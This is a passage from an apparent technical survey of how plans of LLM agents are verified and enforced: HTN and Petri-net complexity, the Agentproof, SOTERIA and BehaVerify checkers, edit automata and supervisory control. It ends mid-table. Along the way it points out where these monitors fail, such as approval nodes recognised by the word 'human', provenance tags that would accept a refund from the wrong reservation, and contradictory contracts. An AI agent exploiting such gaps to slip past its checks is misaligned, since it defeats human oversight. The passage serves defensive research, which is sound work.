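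Most rules about forbidden calls need only Trans. Final matters when stopping halfway does damage, as with the agent that charged a customer's card and never issued the ticket. If the rest of the program is "issue ticket", Final does not hold, and a monitor can detect that the agent is stopping too early. The monitor cannot make the agent continue, but it can alert a person.

When processes run in parallel, small differences in the execution rules matter. In the program φ?; a, the test is a separate step, so another process can act between the test and the action. For example, one process could test that there is no release freeze, another could declare a freeze, and the first could then deploy. ConGolog's `if` prevents this by evaluating the condition and taking the first step of the chosen branch as one indivisible unit. The guarantee applies to the real system only if that system does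 the same.

Comparing notations by their traces does not show when a free choice is made. The programs "a, then b or c" and "a then b, or a then c" allow the same two traces, but the second has already committed to b or to c once it takes step a. A monitor that settles on one branch will refuse a legitimate call from the other, so it has to keep track of both. *An Embedding of ConGolog in 3APL* (Hindriks, Lespérance and Levesque, 2000) therefore compares ConGolog with the agent language 3APL by *bisimulation*, which matches the two languages step by step and so takes account of when each choice happens.

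### What each step up costs

A check made before a plan runs should determine whether any run can end in harm. This is the same problem as deciding whether a plan exists, with the harmful outcome as the goal. Results on plan existence therefore show how hard the check can be.

The table gives the worst case for each notation and assumes that the planning notations have no variables. A PSPACE-complete problem can be solved with memory that grows polynomially with the size of the description, but every known algorithm may take exponential time. An undecidable problem has no algorithm that always gives the right answer.

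| Notation | Trace languages | Can a run reach the goal? |
|---|---|---|
| A fixed sequence of actions | A single word | Polynomial time |
| A finite graph, listed state by state | Regular | Linear time |
| STRIPS | Some regular languages | PSPACE-complete |
| HTN with no ordering at all | Some beyond regular | PSPACE-complete |
| HTN with every method in a fixed order | Context-free | Exponential time |
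| Petri net | Some beyond regular, through counting | Decidable, but Ackermann-complete |
| Unrestricted HTN | Beyond context-free | Undecidable |
| ConGolog with recursive procedures | At least those of HTNs | Undecidable |

STRIPS is less expressive than a finite graph, but it is harder to check because a few facts can describe many states. Thirty facts can describe about a billion states, and a checker may have to search all of them.

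The problem listed for Petri nets is Ackermann-complete, so solving it can take longer than any fixed tower of exponentials. Much of this difficulty comes from the requirement that counts never drop below zero. In *I Always Told My Mom That Order Is Overrated*, Lauer, Zhang and colleagues (2026) studied planning with counters that may go negative, cannot block an action, and have to satisfy conditions only at the end. That problem is PSPACE-complete. A rule that the books must balance at the end of a task is therefore much easier to plan for than a rule that they must balance throughout. These are worst cases for arbitrary questions, though, and the proof that payments never exceed approvals needs no search.

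Erol and colleagues proved that unrestricted HTN planning is undecidable by building a planner's version of a known impossible problem. A context-free grammar is a set of rules that generates words, and no algorithm can decide for every pair of grammars whether they have a word in common. The construction turns both grammars into compound tasks and runs them side by side:

1. For each letter, the first grammar has an action that writes the letter down, and the second has an action that erases it.
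2. A fact called *turn* forces the two grammars to alternate, so each letter must be erased before the next one appears.
3. The second grammar can erase only the letter that the first has just written, so both must spell the same word.

A complete plan exists exactly when the grammars share a word. A planner that could always tell whether a plan exists could therefore always tell whether the grammars share a word, which is impossible. If a plan exists, a systematic search will eventually find it, but if none exists, the search may never end. A safety checker with the same limitation can find a harmful run if there is one, but if it hasn't found one by a given time, one may still exist.

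The construction needs recursion, interleaving and facts that both tasks can read and change. Without recursion, each task can expand only to a limited depth, and the problem is decidable. It is also decidable if every method fixes the order of its tasks, because the steps of two unfinished tasks then cannot be interleaved. Removing all ordering constraints reduces the complexity further. Lauer and colleagues proved that HTN planning is then no harder than STRIPS planning, even though it can still require equal numbers of different actions. Their example is a financial plan in which a series of earning steps must come before the same number of spending steps. ConGolog's recursive procedures and ∥ supply everything the construction needs, so the undecidability carries over.

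Undecidability limits checking a program before it runs more than it limits monitoring the program during the run. To judge a proposed call, a monitor only has to apply Trans to the current program, which is usually easy even if nobody can predict all the program's runs. Researchers have also developed supervisors for such programs. A type checker doesn't answer every case correctly. ELBA's checker, for example, rejects some harmless Haskell programs so that it can guarantee properties of all the ones it accepts.

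### Do agents need plans that are too open to check?

An agent investigating why a website is slow cannot know which logs to read until it has read some. One might conclude that useful agents need plans as open-ended as general programs, and that any notation simple enough to check would restrict them too much to be useful.

A plan that gives an agent more freedom does not need a more expressive notation. A graph with one state and a loop for each tool allows every possible sequence of calls, and it is about the simplest regular plan there is. A notation needs expressive power mainly to exclude runs precisely. Results on *task insertion* support this. If a planner may add primitive tasks anywhere in an HTN plan, the plan can still require certain steps but can no longer forbid extra ones, except through the actions' own preconditions. Höller and colleagues showed that HTNs then cover only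 some of the regular languages. Plan existence also becomes decidable, according to *On the Decidability of HTN Planning with Task Insertion*, so the added freedom makes plans easier to check as well as less expressive.

A plan for the slow website can therefore have a stage in which the agent reads logs and runs harmless queries in any order and for any length of time. The only exit from this stage leads to a second one, where restarting a server uses up an approval. The plan leaves the investigation to the model and limits only actions that can change the system.

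Sub-plans add flexibility. An agent can finish one checked plan, look at the results and write the next, as SOTERIA does at each turn of a conversation. Erol and colleagues studied a similar pattern, in which each method contains at most one compound task and places it last. With this restriction, propositional planning is PSPACE-complete, as it is for STRIPS. Planning can become undecidable when many unfinished tasks interleave, for instance when sub-agents start further sub-agents and all of them share data. A cap on the depth of delegation restores decidability, and few real tasks would need more than a handful of levels. But checking each plan separately does not enforce rules about the whole run. If every new plan starts its count of refunds at zero, an agent can pay one refund per plan without breaking the rule in any of them.

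A step in a plan can also leave a choice to the model, as `llm_eval` does for flights. *SharedKV-BT* (Wake and Wagle, 2026) tested a behaviour tree that works this way. A simulated robot had to put four objects into their bins, and the tree divided the work on each object into acquire, transport and deposit stages. At each stage, the model chose only among the actions and objects that were valid there, and a separate check of the simulator determined whether the stage was complete. The model, Qwen2.5-3B, made the right choice in 113 of 120 recorded situations, compared with 90 when it could see every option at every stage. The robot finished the task in 18 of 30 full runs with the limited options. It never finished with the complete list, because after picking up an object the model kept choosing to pick one up again.

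A model this small makes mistakes more easily than the models behind most current agents, so those models probably won't show a gain of the same size. The experiment still shows that a plan can narrow a model's choices while helping it finish its task. The plan worked because Wake and Wagle knew the three stages in advance. For some work, such as open-ended research, nobody can name the stages beforehand. The plan then comes close to the one-state graph that allows everything, and the protection has to come from the policy specifications and the permissions on individual tools.

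## Checking a plan before it runs

Strict enforcement is only as safe as the plan, so someone has to check the plan before the agent makes its first call. The checks that take the least computation look only at which steps lead to which. They can find a branch that leads nowhere, or a path that reaches a payment without going through the manager. More demanding checks also cover data, such as whether No-Flown returned true for the same reservation that the agent then cancels.

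### Dead ends, exits and approvals

*Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) describes a tool that extracts the workflow graph from an agent's code and checks the graph's shape. The tool works with LangGraph, CrewAI, AutoGen and Google ADK, four frameworks for building agents that each describe workflows differently. It converts their workflows into one kind of graph, whose nodes include tool calls, model calls, routers that choose a branch, and decisions by a person.

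In one example, an agent sorts incoming emails, drafts replies and sends them. A developer adds a drafting step for normal-priority emails but forgets to connect it to the sending step, so the agent drafts replies to those emails but never sends them. A test reveals the mistake only if it includes a normal-priority email. Agentproof finds the mistake without running the agent by detecting that the drafting node has no outgoing edge, and it prints the path to that node.

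Agentproof tests six conditions:

- The agent can reach every exit from the entry.
- From every node that the agent can reach, it can also reach an exit.
- Every node except an exit has an outgoing edge.
- Every edge out of a router has the type "conditional".
- The graph contains at least one decision by a person.
- Every tool node names its tools.

The second condition rules out endless loops, such as agents taking turns brainstorming forever. The fifth is weak because the human node may be on a different branch from the dangerous call. An optional version therefore takes a list of sensitive tools, deletes every human node from the graph, and searches from the entry. If the search still reaches a listed tool, the agent can reach it without anyone's approval. The structural checks took about a tenth of a second on a graph of 5,000 nodes.

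These checks depend on an accurate graph. In LangGraph code, Agentproof treats a node as a human decision if its name contains "human". A human review step without that word in its name causes a false alarm, while a model call named `human_summary` would presumably count as an approval. Xavier and colleagues also want the tool to catch attackers who edit workflow files, but such an attacker could put "human" in the name of a model call.

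### Searching a graph and a rule together

Agentproof turns each rule about the order of steps into a small automaton and searches the graph and the automaton at the same time. For example, the automaton for the rule "after a draft, a human review must come before the next draft" starts in the state *idle*. A draft moves it to *waiting*, and a review moves it back to *idle*. A second draft while it is *waiting* moves it to *violated*.

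Suppose an email agent has this graph, with a shortcut for urgent messages:

```
START  → DRAFT
DRAFT  → REVIEW or SEND
REVIEW → SEND
SEND   → DRAFT or EXIT
```

The search visits pairs of a graph node and an automaton state. In this table, the state in each pair is the one the automaton reaches after processing the node's own step.

| Pair | Pairs that can come next |
|---|---|
| START, *idle* | DRAFT, *waiting* |
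| DRAFT, *waiting* | REVIEW, *idle*; SEND, *waiting* |
| REVIEW, *idle* | SEND, *idle* |
| SEND, *waiting* | DRAFT, *violated*; EXIT, *waiting* |

The search pairs SEND with two automaton states because a draft may legally follow it only if a review has taken place. The search reaches *violated*, and retracing its steps gives the offending path: START, DRAFT, SEND, DRAFT. The graph allows infinitely many runs, but five nodes and three automaton states make at most 15 pairs, so the search always ends. It follows every edge, including any that a guard would block at run time, so it can raise false alarms. Xavier and colleagues did not measure how often this happens.

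The pair EXIT, *waiting* is not a violation. An agent that sends one unreviewed email and stops has obeyed the rule, because no second draft followed. The paper's "Deploy approval" policy has the same form, under which, after a deployment, an approval must come before the next deployment. An agent could obey it by deploying first and getting approval later. The rule language has no operators for the past, so the natural way to test for "approval first" is the check that deletes human nodes. The email graph correctly fails that check, because the agent can still get from DRAFT to SEND without REVIEW.

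Xavier and colleagues tested Agentproof on 18 workflows of 5 to 12 nodes. Five had structural defects and ten failed an approval policy, reported as 27% and 55%. The researchers built the workflows themselves and included known mistakes, so the figures show that the tool finds such defects but don't measure how common they are. The approval policy was the weak version, and the ten workflows that failed it contained no human decision at all. Some of them did low-risk work that hardly needs one.

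### Soundness of workflow nets

Better figures on how often people make such mistakes come from business software. *Soundness of Workflow Nets*, by van der Aalst, van Hee and colleagues, cites a study of more than 2,000 business process models, at least 10% of which had errors such as deadlocks. Among the 604 reference models of the software company SAP, 20.9% had such errors. An agent's workflow graph can go wrong in the same ways.

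The standard test for such models is *soundness*, which van der Aalst defined in *Verification of Workflow Nets*. A workflow net is a Petri net that handles one case, such as an insurance claim. It has a start place and an end place, and everything else lies on a path between them. The case begins with one mark in the start place. The net is sound if it meets three requirements:

1. From every marking that the case can reach, it can still finish with a mark in the end place.
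2. When a mark arrives in the end place, all other places are empty.
3. Every transition can fire in at least one run.

The first requirement resembles Agentproof's second condition. The second requirement matters when steps run in parallel, and it has no counterpart in Agentproof, whose search follows one position at a time. In van der Aalst's example, an insurer checks the customer's policy and contacts the garage in parallel. A joining transition waits for both, and then the insurer either pays or sends a rejection. Suppose a designer replaces the join with a separate transition for each branch. Each branch then delivers its own mark, so the insurer can pay the same claim twice. A search for dead ends finds nothing wrong, because every step still leads to the end. The plan fails the soundness check, however, because a mark is still on the other branch when the first payment finishes the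 case.

To test soundness, van der Aalst adds a transition from the end place back to the start. The original net is sound exactly when the extended net is *live* and *bounded*. In a live net, every transition can always become possible again, and in a bounded net, no place collects marks without limit. The faulty insurance net is unbounded once extended because each round can return more marks to the start than it took out.

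Soundness can be tested in polynomial time for *free-choice* nets, in which any two transitions that share one input place share all their input places. Van der Aalst expected most practical workflows to be checkable in polynomial time. Blondin, Mazowiecki and Offtermatt proved in *The complexity of soundness in workflow nets* (2022) that the problem is EXPSPACE-complete for workflow nets in general, so a checker may need memory that grows exponentially with the size of the net. The problem becomes undecidable if a transition can also empty a place regardless of how many marks it holds, which is a common way to model cancellation.

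Agents run into this last difficulty when a late failure sends work back to an earlier step. Say a failed test returns the code to the writing step, which gets a fresh set of attempts. Resetting the number of attempts has the same effect as emptying and refilling a place. Bhardwaj, Singh and Bhardwaj (2026), in *Bounded Loops*, therefore prove that such workflows end only under certain conditions. The most important is that all repairs draw on one shared budget. If each step had its own repair budget, two steps could go on repairing each other for ever, each restoring what the other had used. With R repairs in total and at most mᵥ attempts at each step v, the whole run makes at most

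(R + 1) · Σᵥ mᵥ

attempts. Three steps with three attempts each and two repairs make at most 27, which an operator can calculate before starting the agent.

Many agents have no graph to check. *From Agent Loops to Structured Graphs* (2026) surveyed 70 open-source agent projects. According to Bhardwaj and colleagues, 42 of them used some form of the plain loop in which the model picks every next step.

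### From shape to data

Van der Aalst deliberately left data out and treated every branch as a free choice, because people and other software set the data. This model is too coarse for the airline's first rule. A graph search can confirm that every path to DO_CANCEL passes through CHECK_FLOWN, but it would also accept a plan that runs the check and cancels regardless of the result.

*Lean4Agent* (Wang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) includes some data in the check by giving each step of a workflow conditions that must hold before it and conditions that should hold after it. The proof assistant Lean then checks that earlier steps supply what later steps need, so it rejects a workflow in which a step reads a field that no earlier step has written. For the model's own steps, the proof generously assumes that if the conditions before a step hold, the model can make the conditions after it hold.

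Workflows that passed the check outperformed those that failed by an average of 14.80% on hard software bugs and 9.07% on questions about AI papers. A language model wrote all the workflows, and a carefully written one is probably more likely both to pass the check and to succeed at the task. The gap therefore suggests that the check can be used to pick out good workflows, but not that it improves them.

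### How SOTERIA proves that a plan obeys the rules

SOTERIA checks a plan for all possible inputs at once. For each state s, it builds a formula Σ(s), the *symbolic state*, which covers every combination of values that the variables can have when the plan reaches s. A transition adds its guard to the formula, and a tool call adds the postcondition from the tool's contract. Where two branches meet, SOTERIA joins their formulas with "or". It then passes three kinds of claim to Dafny, an automatic program verifier:

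- *Tool contracts.* If the plan calls tool a with arguments v under guard g, then Σ(s) ∧ g ⇒ Pₐ(v), where Pₐ is the tool's precondition.
- *Progress.* Some run can reach each non-terminal state, so Σ(s) is satisfiable. Wherever the plan branches, at least one guard is true, so Σ(s) ⇒ g₁ ∨ … ∨ gₙ.
- *Policy compliance.* Every policy specification holds at the end of every path.

The third kind of claim is about the history of the run, which the plan's variables do not record. SOTERIA therefore adds bookkeeping that exists only in the proof, including a step counter and, for every tool that a specification mentions, a log of calls with their arguments and results.

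Take the faulty plan for RES123, which never calls No-Flown. The table shows what the proof has collected on arrival at each state.

| State | What Σ gains | Log of No-Flown | Log of Cancel-Resv |
|---|---|---|---|
| LOOKUP | The plan's inputs are valid | empty | empty |
| CHECK_AGE | `resv` meets Get-Resv's postcondition | empty | empty |
| CHECK_RULES | `hrs` meets Hours-Diff's postcondition | empty | empty |
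| DO_CANCEL | `hrs` ≤ 24 | empty | empty |
| DONE | The result meets Cancel-Resv's postcondition | empty | one call, on `rid`, at step 2 |
| NOT_PERMITTED | `hrs` > 24 | empty | empty |

The progress check passes at CHECK_RULES, because `hrs` is always either at most 24 or more than 24. The policy check comes at the two terminal states. There, for every call c in the log of Cancel-Resv, the log of No-Flown must contain a call d such that

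d.step < c.step, d.rid = c.rid and d.result = true

At NOT_PERMITTED, the Cancel-Resv log is empty, so the claim holds trivially. At DONE, the Cancel-Resv log contains one call but the No-Flown log is empty, so no d exists and the proof fails. SOTERIA rejects the plan before the agent calls any tool and reports to the planner which specification failed. The planner can then try again, up to eight times in the main experiments.

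In the corrected plan, No-Flown runs at step 1 and Cancel-Resv at step 3, both on `rid`, and the guard at CHECK_AGE adds the fact that `ok` is true. The claim now holds for every reservation number and booking time. Without that guard, the logs would have the same calls in the same order, but Σ would also allow `ok` to be false. The proof would then fail, exposing a mistake that a search of the graph's shape cannot detect.

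Because the claims come at the end of each path, they can also cover steps that must happen later, such as reading a file back after writing it.

Some rules restrict where a value can come from, such as the airline's rule that a refund amount must derive from a lookup of the same reservation. For each variable, the proof records which tools' results contributed to its current value, so an amount computed from `resv` has the tag "Get-Resv.result" and a constant written by the planner has no tag. Two calls to the same tool produce the same tag. If a plan looked up both RES123 and RES456, computed the amount from RES456 and refunded RES123, it would apparently still pass the proof's check, because the amount has the right tag and the log contains a lookup of RES123.

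### Proving sub-plans separately

When a plan calls a sub-plan, SOTERIA proves that the sub-plan's precondition holds at the call and then assumes its postcondition, without checking the sub-plan's internal states. The sub-plan has its own proof, which SOTERIA reuses for every customer.

He et al. measured the effect on the airline tasks with GPT-5.4-mini as the planner. In one setup, the planner could call sub-plans from a library, and in the other, it had to write out every procedure in full.

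| | With sub-plans | Without |
|---|---|---|
| Planning turns that produced a verified plan | 65 of 68 | 38 of 60 |
| Verified on the first attempt | 48.5% | 23.3% |
| Median number of states in a plan | 8 | 11 |

Sub-plans also changed the kinds of errors that remained. Without them, the planner often violated a policy specification and kept doing so on later attempts, because the repair required a different plan. With them, most of the remaining failures were syntax errors in the plan, which the planner could fix from the error message. A stronger planner would probably need the library less, but the experiment tested only this small model.

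### Behaviour trees in a model checker

A behaviour tree may tick forever, so a proof that works through the states once, in order, does not suit it. *BehaVerify* (Serbinowska, Wooding and colleagues, 2026) instead uses a model checker, a program that searches all the reachable states of a finite system. The user writes one file containing the tree, its variables, the ways the environment can change between ticks, and the properties to check. BehaVerify translates the file for the model checker nuXmv, which either confirms a property or returns a run that violates it.

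In a small example, a drone moves one square at a time on a grid, in a direction the tree leaves open. The property "the drone always eventually reaches its goal" is false, and nuXmv can return a run in which the drone flies north and south forever. The property "the drone can always still reach its goal" is true. The first kind of property describes what happens in every run, and the second what remains possible. An agent's designer may need both, for instance to check that no run includes the same payment twice and that a handover to a person always remains possible.

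A direct translation takes one transition for each node that a tick visits, so two ticks of the drone's small tree take 15 transitions. BehaVerify's encoding, called *fastforwarding*, computes the result of a whole tick in a single transition. If a variable changes several times within a tick, the encoding defines each later value by a formula over the earlier ones. These formulas add no states unless the tree makes a free choice, and properties can still refer to the intermediate values.

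Serbinowska and colleagues ran both encodings on the same trees with a five-minute limit. CTL and LTL are logics for stating properties. CTL can express what remains possible, while LTL describes single runs.

| Nodes in the tree | CTL, fastforwarding | CTL, direct | LTL, fastforwarding | LTL, direct |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 71 | 0.02 s | 0.62 s | 0.38 s | 3.54 s |
| 263 | 0.11 s | 53.03 s | 4.27 s | over 5 min |
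| 2,055 | 2.24 s | over 5 min | 153.65 s | over 5 min |

An earlier paper on the same tool, *Formalizing Stateful Behavior Trees* (2024), reports 8.20 seconds for a tree of 10,000 nodes and 32.32 seconds for one of 20,000. An airline procedure needs far fewer nodes. But the test trees had few variables, and the number of states depends on the variables and how many values each can take, not on the number of nodes. A tree of little more than 30 nodes, for a drone flying in three dimensions, took 86.87 seconds for one property. After the researchers rewrote the tree to need less memory of past ticks, the same property took 0.48 seconds.

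A language-model agent's reservation numbers and messages would have to be grouped into a few categories before nuXmv could search them all. SOTERIA's formulas cover all reservation numbers at once, but its plans cannot repeat steps, while nuXmv can check plans that do.

The drone tree also contained a bug that an earlier tool's published checks had missed because they included no property about the battery. The drone should land when the battery is critical. But the tree stores which child was still running, so if a low battery has already started a navigation step, the next tick resumes that step and skips the battery checks.

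BehaVerify can include a small neural network in the tree. For a drone on a 10 × 10 grid, it ran the network on all 10,000 combinations of position and goal and stored the answers as a table. One network chose the right move for 99.95% of its training data, but nuXmv still found a run in which the drone stopped and never reached its target. No one can tabulate a language model this way, so when a SOTERIA plan leaves a choice to the model through `llm_eval`, the proof allows for any answer that meets the stated condition.

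### What the proofs take for granted

SOTERIA's proofs assume that the tool contracts are true. If No-Flown checked only the outbound flight, although its contract covers the whole trip, Dafny would still accept the corrected plan, and the agent could cancel a half-used ticket. The run-time check of postconditions would not catch the error, because a wrong "true" looks the same as a right one. A contract that contradicts itself is worse, because anything can be proved from it. The progress check catches this in most places, since no run could reach the next state. But He and colleagues describe that check only for non-terminal states, so a contradictory contract for Cancel-Resv, the last call before DONE, might let even the faulty plan pass.

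The proofs also require plans without loops. SOTERIA works through the states in order, and a cycle has no first state. Program verifiers can handle loops if someone supplies a statement that stays true on every pass, but SOTERIA does not require its planner to provide one. To search until it finds a suitable flight, the agent would need a new plan for each round.

The solver behind Dafny may not finish, even when a plan is correct and has no loops. SOTERIA gives it ten seconds per state. A timeout doesn't show whether the plan is correct, so SOTERIA counts the plan as unverified. Strict mode will then refuse to run it. The customer may be denied a legitimate cancellation as a result, but the airline's rules are not broken.

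A proof covers only the runs that the plan allows, and only the rules as written. When He and colleagues gave agents a flat plan without a monitor, GPT-5.4-mini broke the airline's rules 13 times in 50 tasks. It still broke the rules 10 times when SOTERIA also tried to verify the plans, because nothing forced the model to follow a plan that had passed verification.

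## What a run-time check can enforce

A proof that every path through a plan reads a file back after writing it doesn't stop an agent from writing the file and ending the run there. A run-time monitor also has trouble enforcing this rule, because when the agent proposes the write, the monitor can't foresee the later read or make the agent perform it. The monitor can refuse a cancellation if the agent hasn't made the No-Flown check first, because the trace already shows whether it did.

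### Safety and liveness

The theory of enforcement rests on two definitions. Both allow traces that never end, as well as finite ones.

- A rule is a *safety property* if every trace that breaks it has a finite beginning after which no continuation can satisfy the rule.
- A rule is a *liveness property* if every finite trace has some continuation that satisfies the rule.

"No cancellation without an earlier No-Flown check" is a safety property, because no later call can repair a cancellation that lacked the check. "After writing a file, read it back" is a liveness property, because the agent can still go back and read any files it has left unread.

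Alpern and Schneider proved in the 1980s that every rule about single traces combines a safety property with a liveness property. Adding a deadline to the read-back rule produces such a mixture. *Edit Automata* (Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, 2003) makes the same point about a similar rule for releasing resources. Suppose the agent has ten calls to read the file. If it makes an eleventh call without having read the file, it has permanently broken the rule. If it stops after eight calls without having read the file, it has also broken the rule, but it could have complied by continuing.

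Some policies depend on more than one run. Noninterference compares two, because whether an email leaks a salary depends on what the agent would have sent if the salary had been different. A monitor sees only one run, so it can prevent leaks only by enforcing a stricter rule about single runs, and that rule will also block some runs that leak nothing.

### Why stopping a run enforces only safety

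Schneider (2000), in *Enforceable Security Policies*, studied monitors that watch the steps of a program and end the run when the next step would break a policy. Firewalls and most operating-system protections work this way. These monitors don't analyse the program's code, so they know only what has happened so far. The argument that they can enforce nothing beyond safety properties has three premises:

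1. The monitor judges each run by itself. The policy must therefore be a rule about single traces.
2. The monitor cannot see the future, and the run might end at any moment. If the trace so far breaks the rule, the monitor must already have stopped it, even if a later step would have put things right. The rule must therefore be one that no later step can repair.
3. The monitor rejects a bad run after finitely many steps. Every trace that breaks the rule must therefore have a finite beginning that already breaks it.

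Together, these requirements define a safety property. The read-back rule fails the second requirement. A trace that ends just after a write breaks the rule, so the monitor would have to forbid the write, even for agents that were about to read the file back.

Schneider describes monitors for safety properties as *security automata*. The automaton for "send no messages after reading a file" has two states. It starts in a state that allows every step, and reading a file moves it to a state with no transition for sending. The monitor runs the automaton alongside the program and stops the program if the automaton has no transition for the next step. Agent monitors instead refuse the step and let the program try another, which does not enlarge the set of enforceable policies.

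An automaton can block every action but one, but it cannot force a program to take that action. In one of Schneider's examples, a seller who has received a payment is allowed only to deliver the service, but can still stop altogether and keep the money. Similarly, once an agent has written a file, a monitor could refuse every call except one to read it, but the agent could still end the run.

### Holding actions back and adding new ones

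The limit to safety properties applies to monitors that can only stop the program. Ligatti and colleagues defined the *edit automaton*, a monitor that can also suppress an action without stopping the program, or insert an action that the program did not request. They call a monitor *sound* if everything that reaches the outside world obeys the rule, and *transparent* if it preserves the meaning of any run that already obeys the rule. Without the transparency requirement, a monitor could enforce most rules by blocking everything.

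An edit automaton can enforce the read-back rule for a single file. When the agent writes the file, the monitor holds the write back and tells the agent that the write succeeded. When the agent asks to read the file, the monitor performs the write and then the read. If the agent never asks to read the file, the write never happens. Databases similarly hide a transaction's changes until the transaction is complete.

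Ligatti, Bauer and Walker (2005), in *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors*, identify rules that an edit automaton can enforce. They call a rule a *renewal property* if an infinite trace obeys it exactly when infinitely many of its finite beginnings do. An edit automaton can enforce any renewal property that the empty trace obeys, provided a program can decide whether any given finite trace obeys it. Renewal properties include every safety property and some liveness properties, such as "a program that does anything must eventually run an audit".

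With two files, the read-back rule is no longer a renewal property. An agent might write A, write B, read A, write A again, read B, and so on forever. It reads back everything it writes, but after the first write there is always an unread file. A monitor that waits for a moment when the trace obeys the rule would hold back the writes forever. So no edit automaton can enforce the rule if it must output compliant runs unchanged.

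If extra reads are harmless, the monitor can avoid the problem by inserting a read after every write. This satisfies the wording of the rule for any number of files. But if the rule is meant to help the agent notice failed writes, the monitor must also show the agent the result of each read.

Holding an action back works less well for agents than for databases. If the agent runs its tests between the write and the read, the tests will use the old file. A monitor can't hold back some other actions at all. Ligatti and colleagues point out that it can't pretend to send an email, wait for the reply and then decide whether to send the email.

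*What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) proves that a monitor that decides on each call just before it takes irreversible effect can enforce only safety properties, and only those whose permitted traces it can recognise with the memory it has. The paper's example of a rule such a monitor can't enforce is "every payment is eventually followed by a confirmation". If the monitor allows the payment, the confirmation may never come, but if it refuses, it blocks agents that would have confirmed. Letting the monitor substitute one call for another doesn't change this. Schneider's limit therefore applies again for payments, emails and deployments.

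### Refusing to let the agent finish

An agent's run usually ends when the model replies without a tool call. The developer can instead make finishing a call of its own, named `done`, which the monitor can refuse. The rule "no `done` while a written file is unread" is a safety property, because a write followed by `done` with no read in between is a violation that nothing later can repair. For one file, the automaton has two states:

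| State | Write | Read | `done` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing to check | Go to "file unread" | Stay | Allow |
| File unread | Stay | Go to "nothing to check" | Refuse |

When there are several files, the monitor keeps a list of the unread ones and allows `done` only when the list is empty. It doesn't need to hold back a write or falsely report that one succeeded.

*MENTOR*, a monitor described by Anand, Chatzi and colleagues (2026), uses this method. It turns a company's procedures into formal rules. While an obligation is unfulfilled, it rejects `done` and suggests a call that would help fulfil the obligation. A failed attempt does not count, so an agent that has to book a flight still has that obligation after the booking tool returns an error.

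ContrAgent, the system presented in Xiao, Liu and Nuzzo's *Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (2026), handles obligations in two ways. If a rule requires a read as the next action, ContrAgent blocks any other action. If the rule requires the read only at some later point, ContrAgent keeps the obligation pending, reminds the agent at the end of the session, and records a failure if the agent still doesn't perform the read.

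Refusing `done` enforces a weaker rule than the original. The agent must read its files back before it can finish properly, but it can also crash, use up its budget or keep making other calls. In tests on the MANTRA benchmark, where agents could make at most 40 calls, MENTOR also stopped refusing `done` after 25, even if duties were still open. A developer who relies on the rule would have to treat runs that end with duties open as failures.

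The refusal can also leave an agent with no way to finish. Suppose the user withdraws access to a file after the agent has written it but before the agent has read it. One rule now forbids the read, and another forbids `done` until the file has been read. The agent could finish under either rule alone. The monitor cannot refuse the user's decision, so it could prevent this only by refusing the write. A more sensible solution is for the rules to let the agent finish by reporting that the file is unread. Anand and colleagues require their formulas to state such exceptions, so the obligation becomes "eventually read the file, or eventually meet the condition that waives the read".

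### Events that the monitor cannot refuse

Schneider's argument also assumes that the monitor can prevent the next step. That assumption fails for a rule such as "nobody may be denied the resource for more than 60 seconds". The rule is a safety property, since a wait of 61 seconds can't be undone, but a monitor can't stop time from passing. If the limit were 60 program steps, the monitor could enforce it by halting the program. Basin et al. (2012) refined Schneider's theory to distinguish actions a monitor can prevent from those it can only observe.

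In 1987, the control theorists Ramadge and Wonham introduced *supervisory control*, a way to compute what a monitor should do when it can prevent some events but not others. They developed it for systems such as factories, where a controller can decide whether to start a machine but not whether the machine breaks down. For an agent, only its own tool calls are controllable.

The method starts from a finite list of states, some of them forbidden and some of them terminal, meaning that the task is over. A supervisor specifies which events may happen in each state, and it must always permit the uncontrollable ones. It is safe if no permitted run reaches a forbidden state. It is *nonblocking* if, from every state that a permitted run can reach, some permitted continuation leads to a terminal state. The computation removes states until only acceptable ones are left:

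1. Remove the forbidden states.
2. Remove every state from which an uncontrollable event leads to a removed state. Repeat until nothing changes.
3. Remove every state from which no path through the remaining states reaches a terminal state.
4. If step 3 removed anything, go back to step 2, because an uncontrollable event may now lead to a newly removed state.

The result is called a *fixed point* because applying the steps again changes nothing. The supervisor permits a controllable event exactly when it leads to a remaining state. If the computation has removed the starting state, no safe and nonblocking supervisor exists.

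The resulting supervisor is also *maximally permissive*, meaning it permits every event that any other safe and nonblocking supervisor permits. For any safe and nonblocking supervisor, no uncontrollable event leads out of the set of states it can reach, and every state in that set can reach a terminal state without leaving the set. The computation never removes a state from a set with these two properties, so it keeps every state that a safe and nonblocking supervisor could use.

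### A supervisor computed by hand

Suppose an agent can start a software rollout, which then finishes by itself and puts the new version online. An incident can freeze releases at any time, and the freeze later ends. No version may go live during a freeze.

As a Petri net, this has one mark for the progress of the release and another that moves between "no freeze" and "frozen". Freezes no longer matter once the version is online, so six states are enough:

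| State | What the agent can do | What can happen anyway |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Ready, no freeze (the starting state) | Start the rollout → 3 | Incident → 2 |
| 2. Ready, frozen | Nothing | Freeze ends → 1 |
| 3. Rolling out, no freeze | Nothing | Incident → 4; rollout finishes → 5 |
| 4. Rolling out, frozen | Nothing | Freeze ends → 3; rollout finishes → 6 |
| 5. Live (terminal) | Nothing | Nothing relevant |
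| 6. Went live during a freeze (forbidden) | Nothing | Nothing relevant |

The computation first removes state 6. It then removes state 4, because the rollout can finish there and lead to state 6. Next it removes state 3, because an incident leads from there to state 4. This leaves states 1, 2 and 5, and no uncontrollable event leads out of this set. A supervisor could therefore keep the agent safe by never letting it start a rollout.

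Without a rollout, states 1 and 2 cannot reach state 5, so step 3 removes both. One of them is the starting state, so no supervisor can be both safe and nonblocking. Checking for a freeze just before the rollout would not help, because the incident can come afterwards.

Suppose the rollout now ends in a staging area, and the agent has to publish the new version with a separate call. The net gains two states, "staged, no freeze" and "staged, frozen", and the only way into the forbidden state is to publish during a freeze. Because the monitor can refuse that call, the computation removes only the forbidden state. Every other state can still reach "live", if necessary by waiting for the freeze to end. The resulting supervisor blocks only publishing during a freeze.

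### The full release agent

The net that Gu and Zhu analyse in *Certified Execution Harness for Agentic AI* adds tests, a security scan, a reviewer's approval and a limited release window. It has 20 places and 18 transitions. They computed the supervisor for five versions:

| Version of the net | Reachable markings | Does the supervisor ever allow a deployment? |
|---|---|---|
| The rollout goes live when it finishes, the monitor can refuse the finish, and freezes never end | 27 | No |
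| The same, but the agent can abort a frozen rollout | 28 | No |
| The same, but freezes can also end | 30 | Yes |
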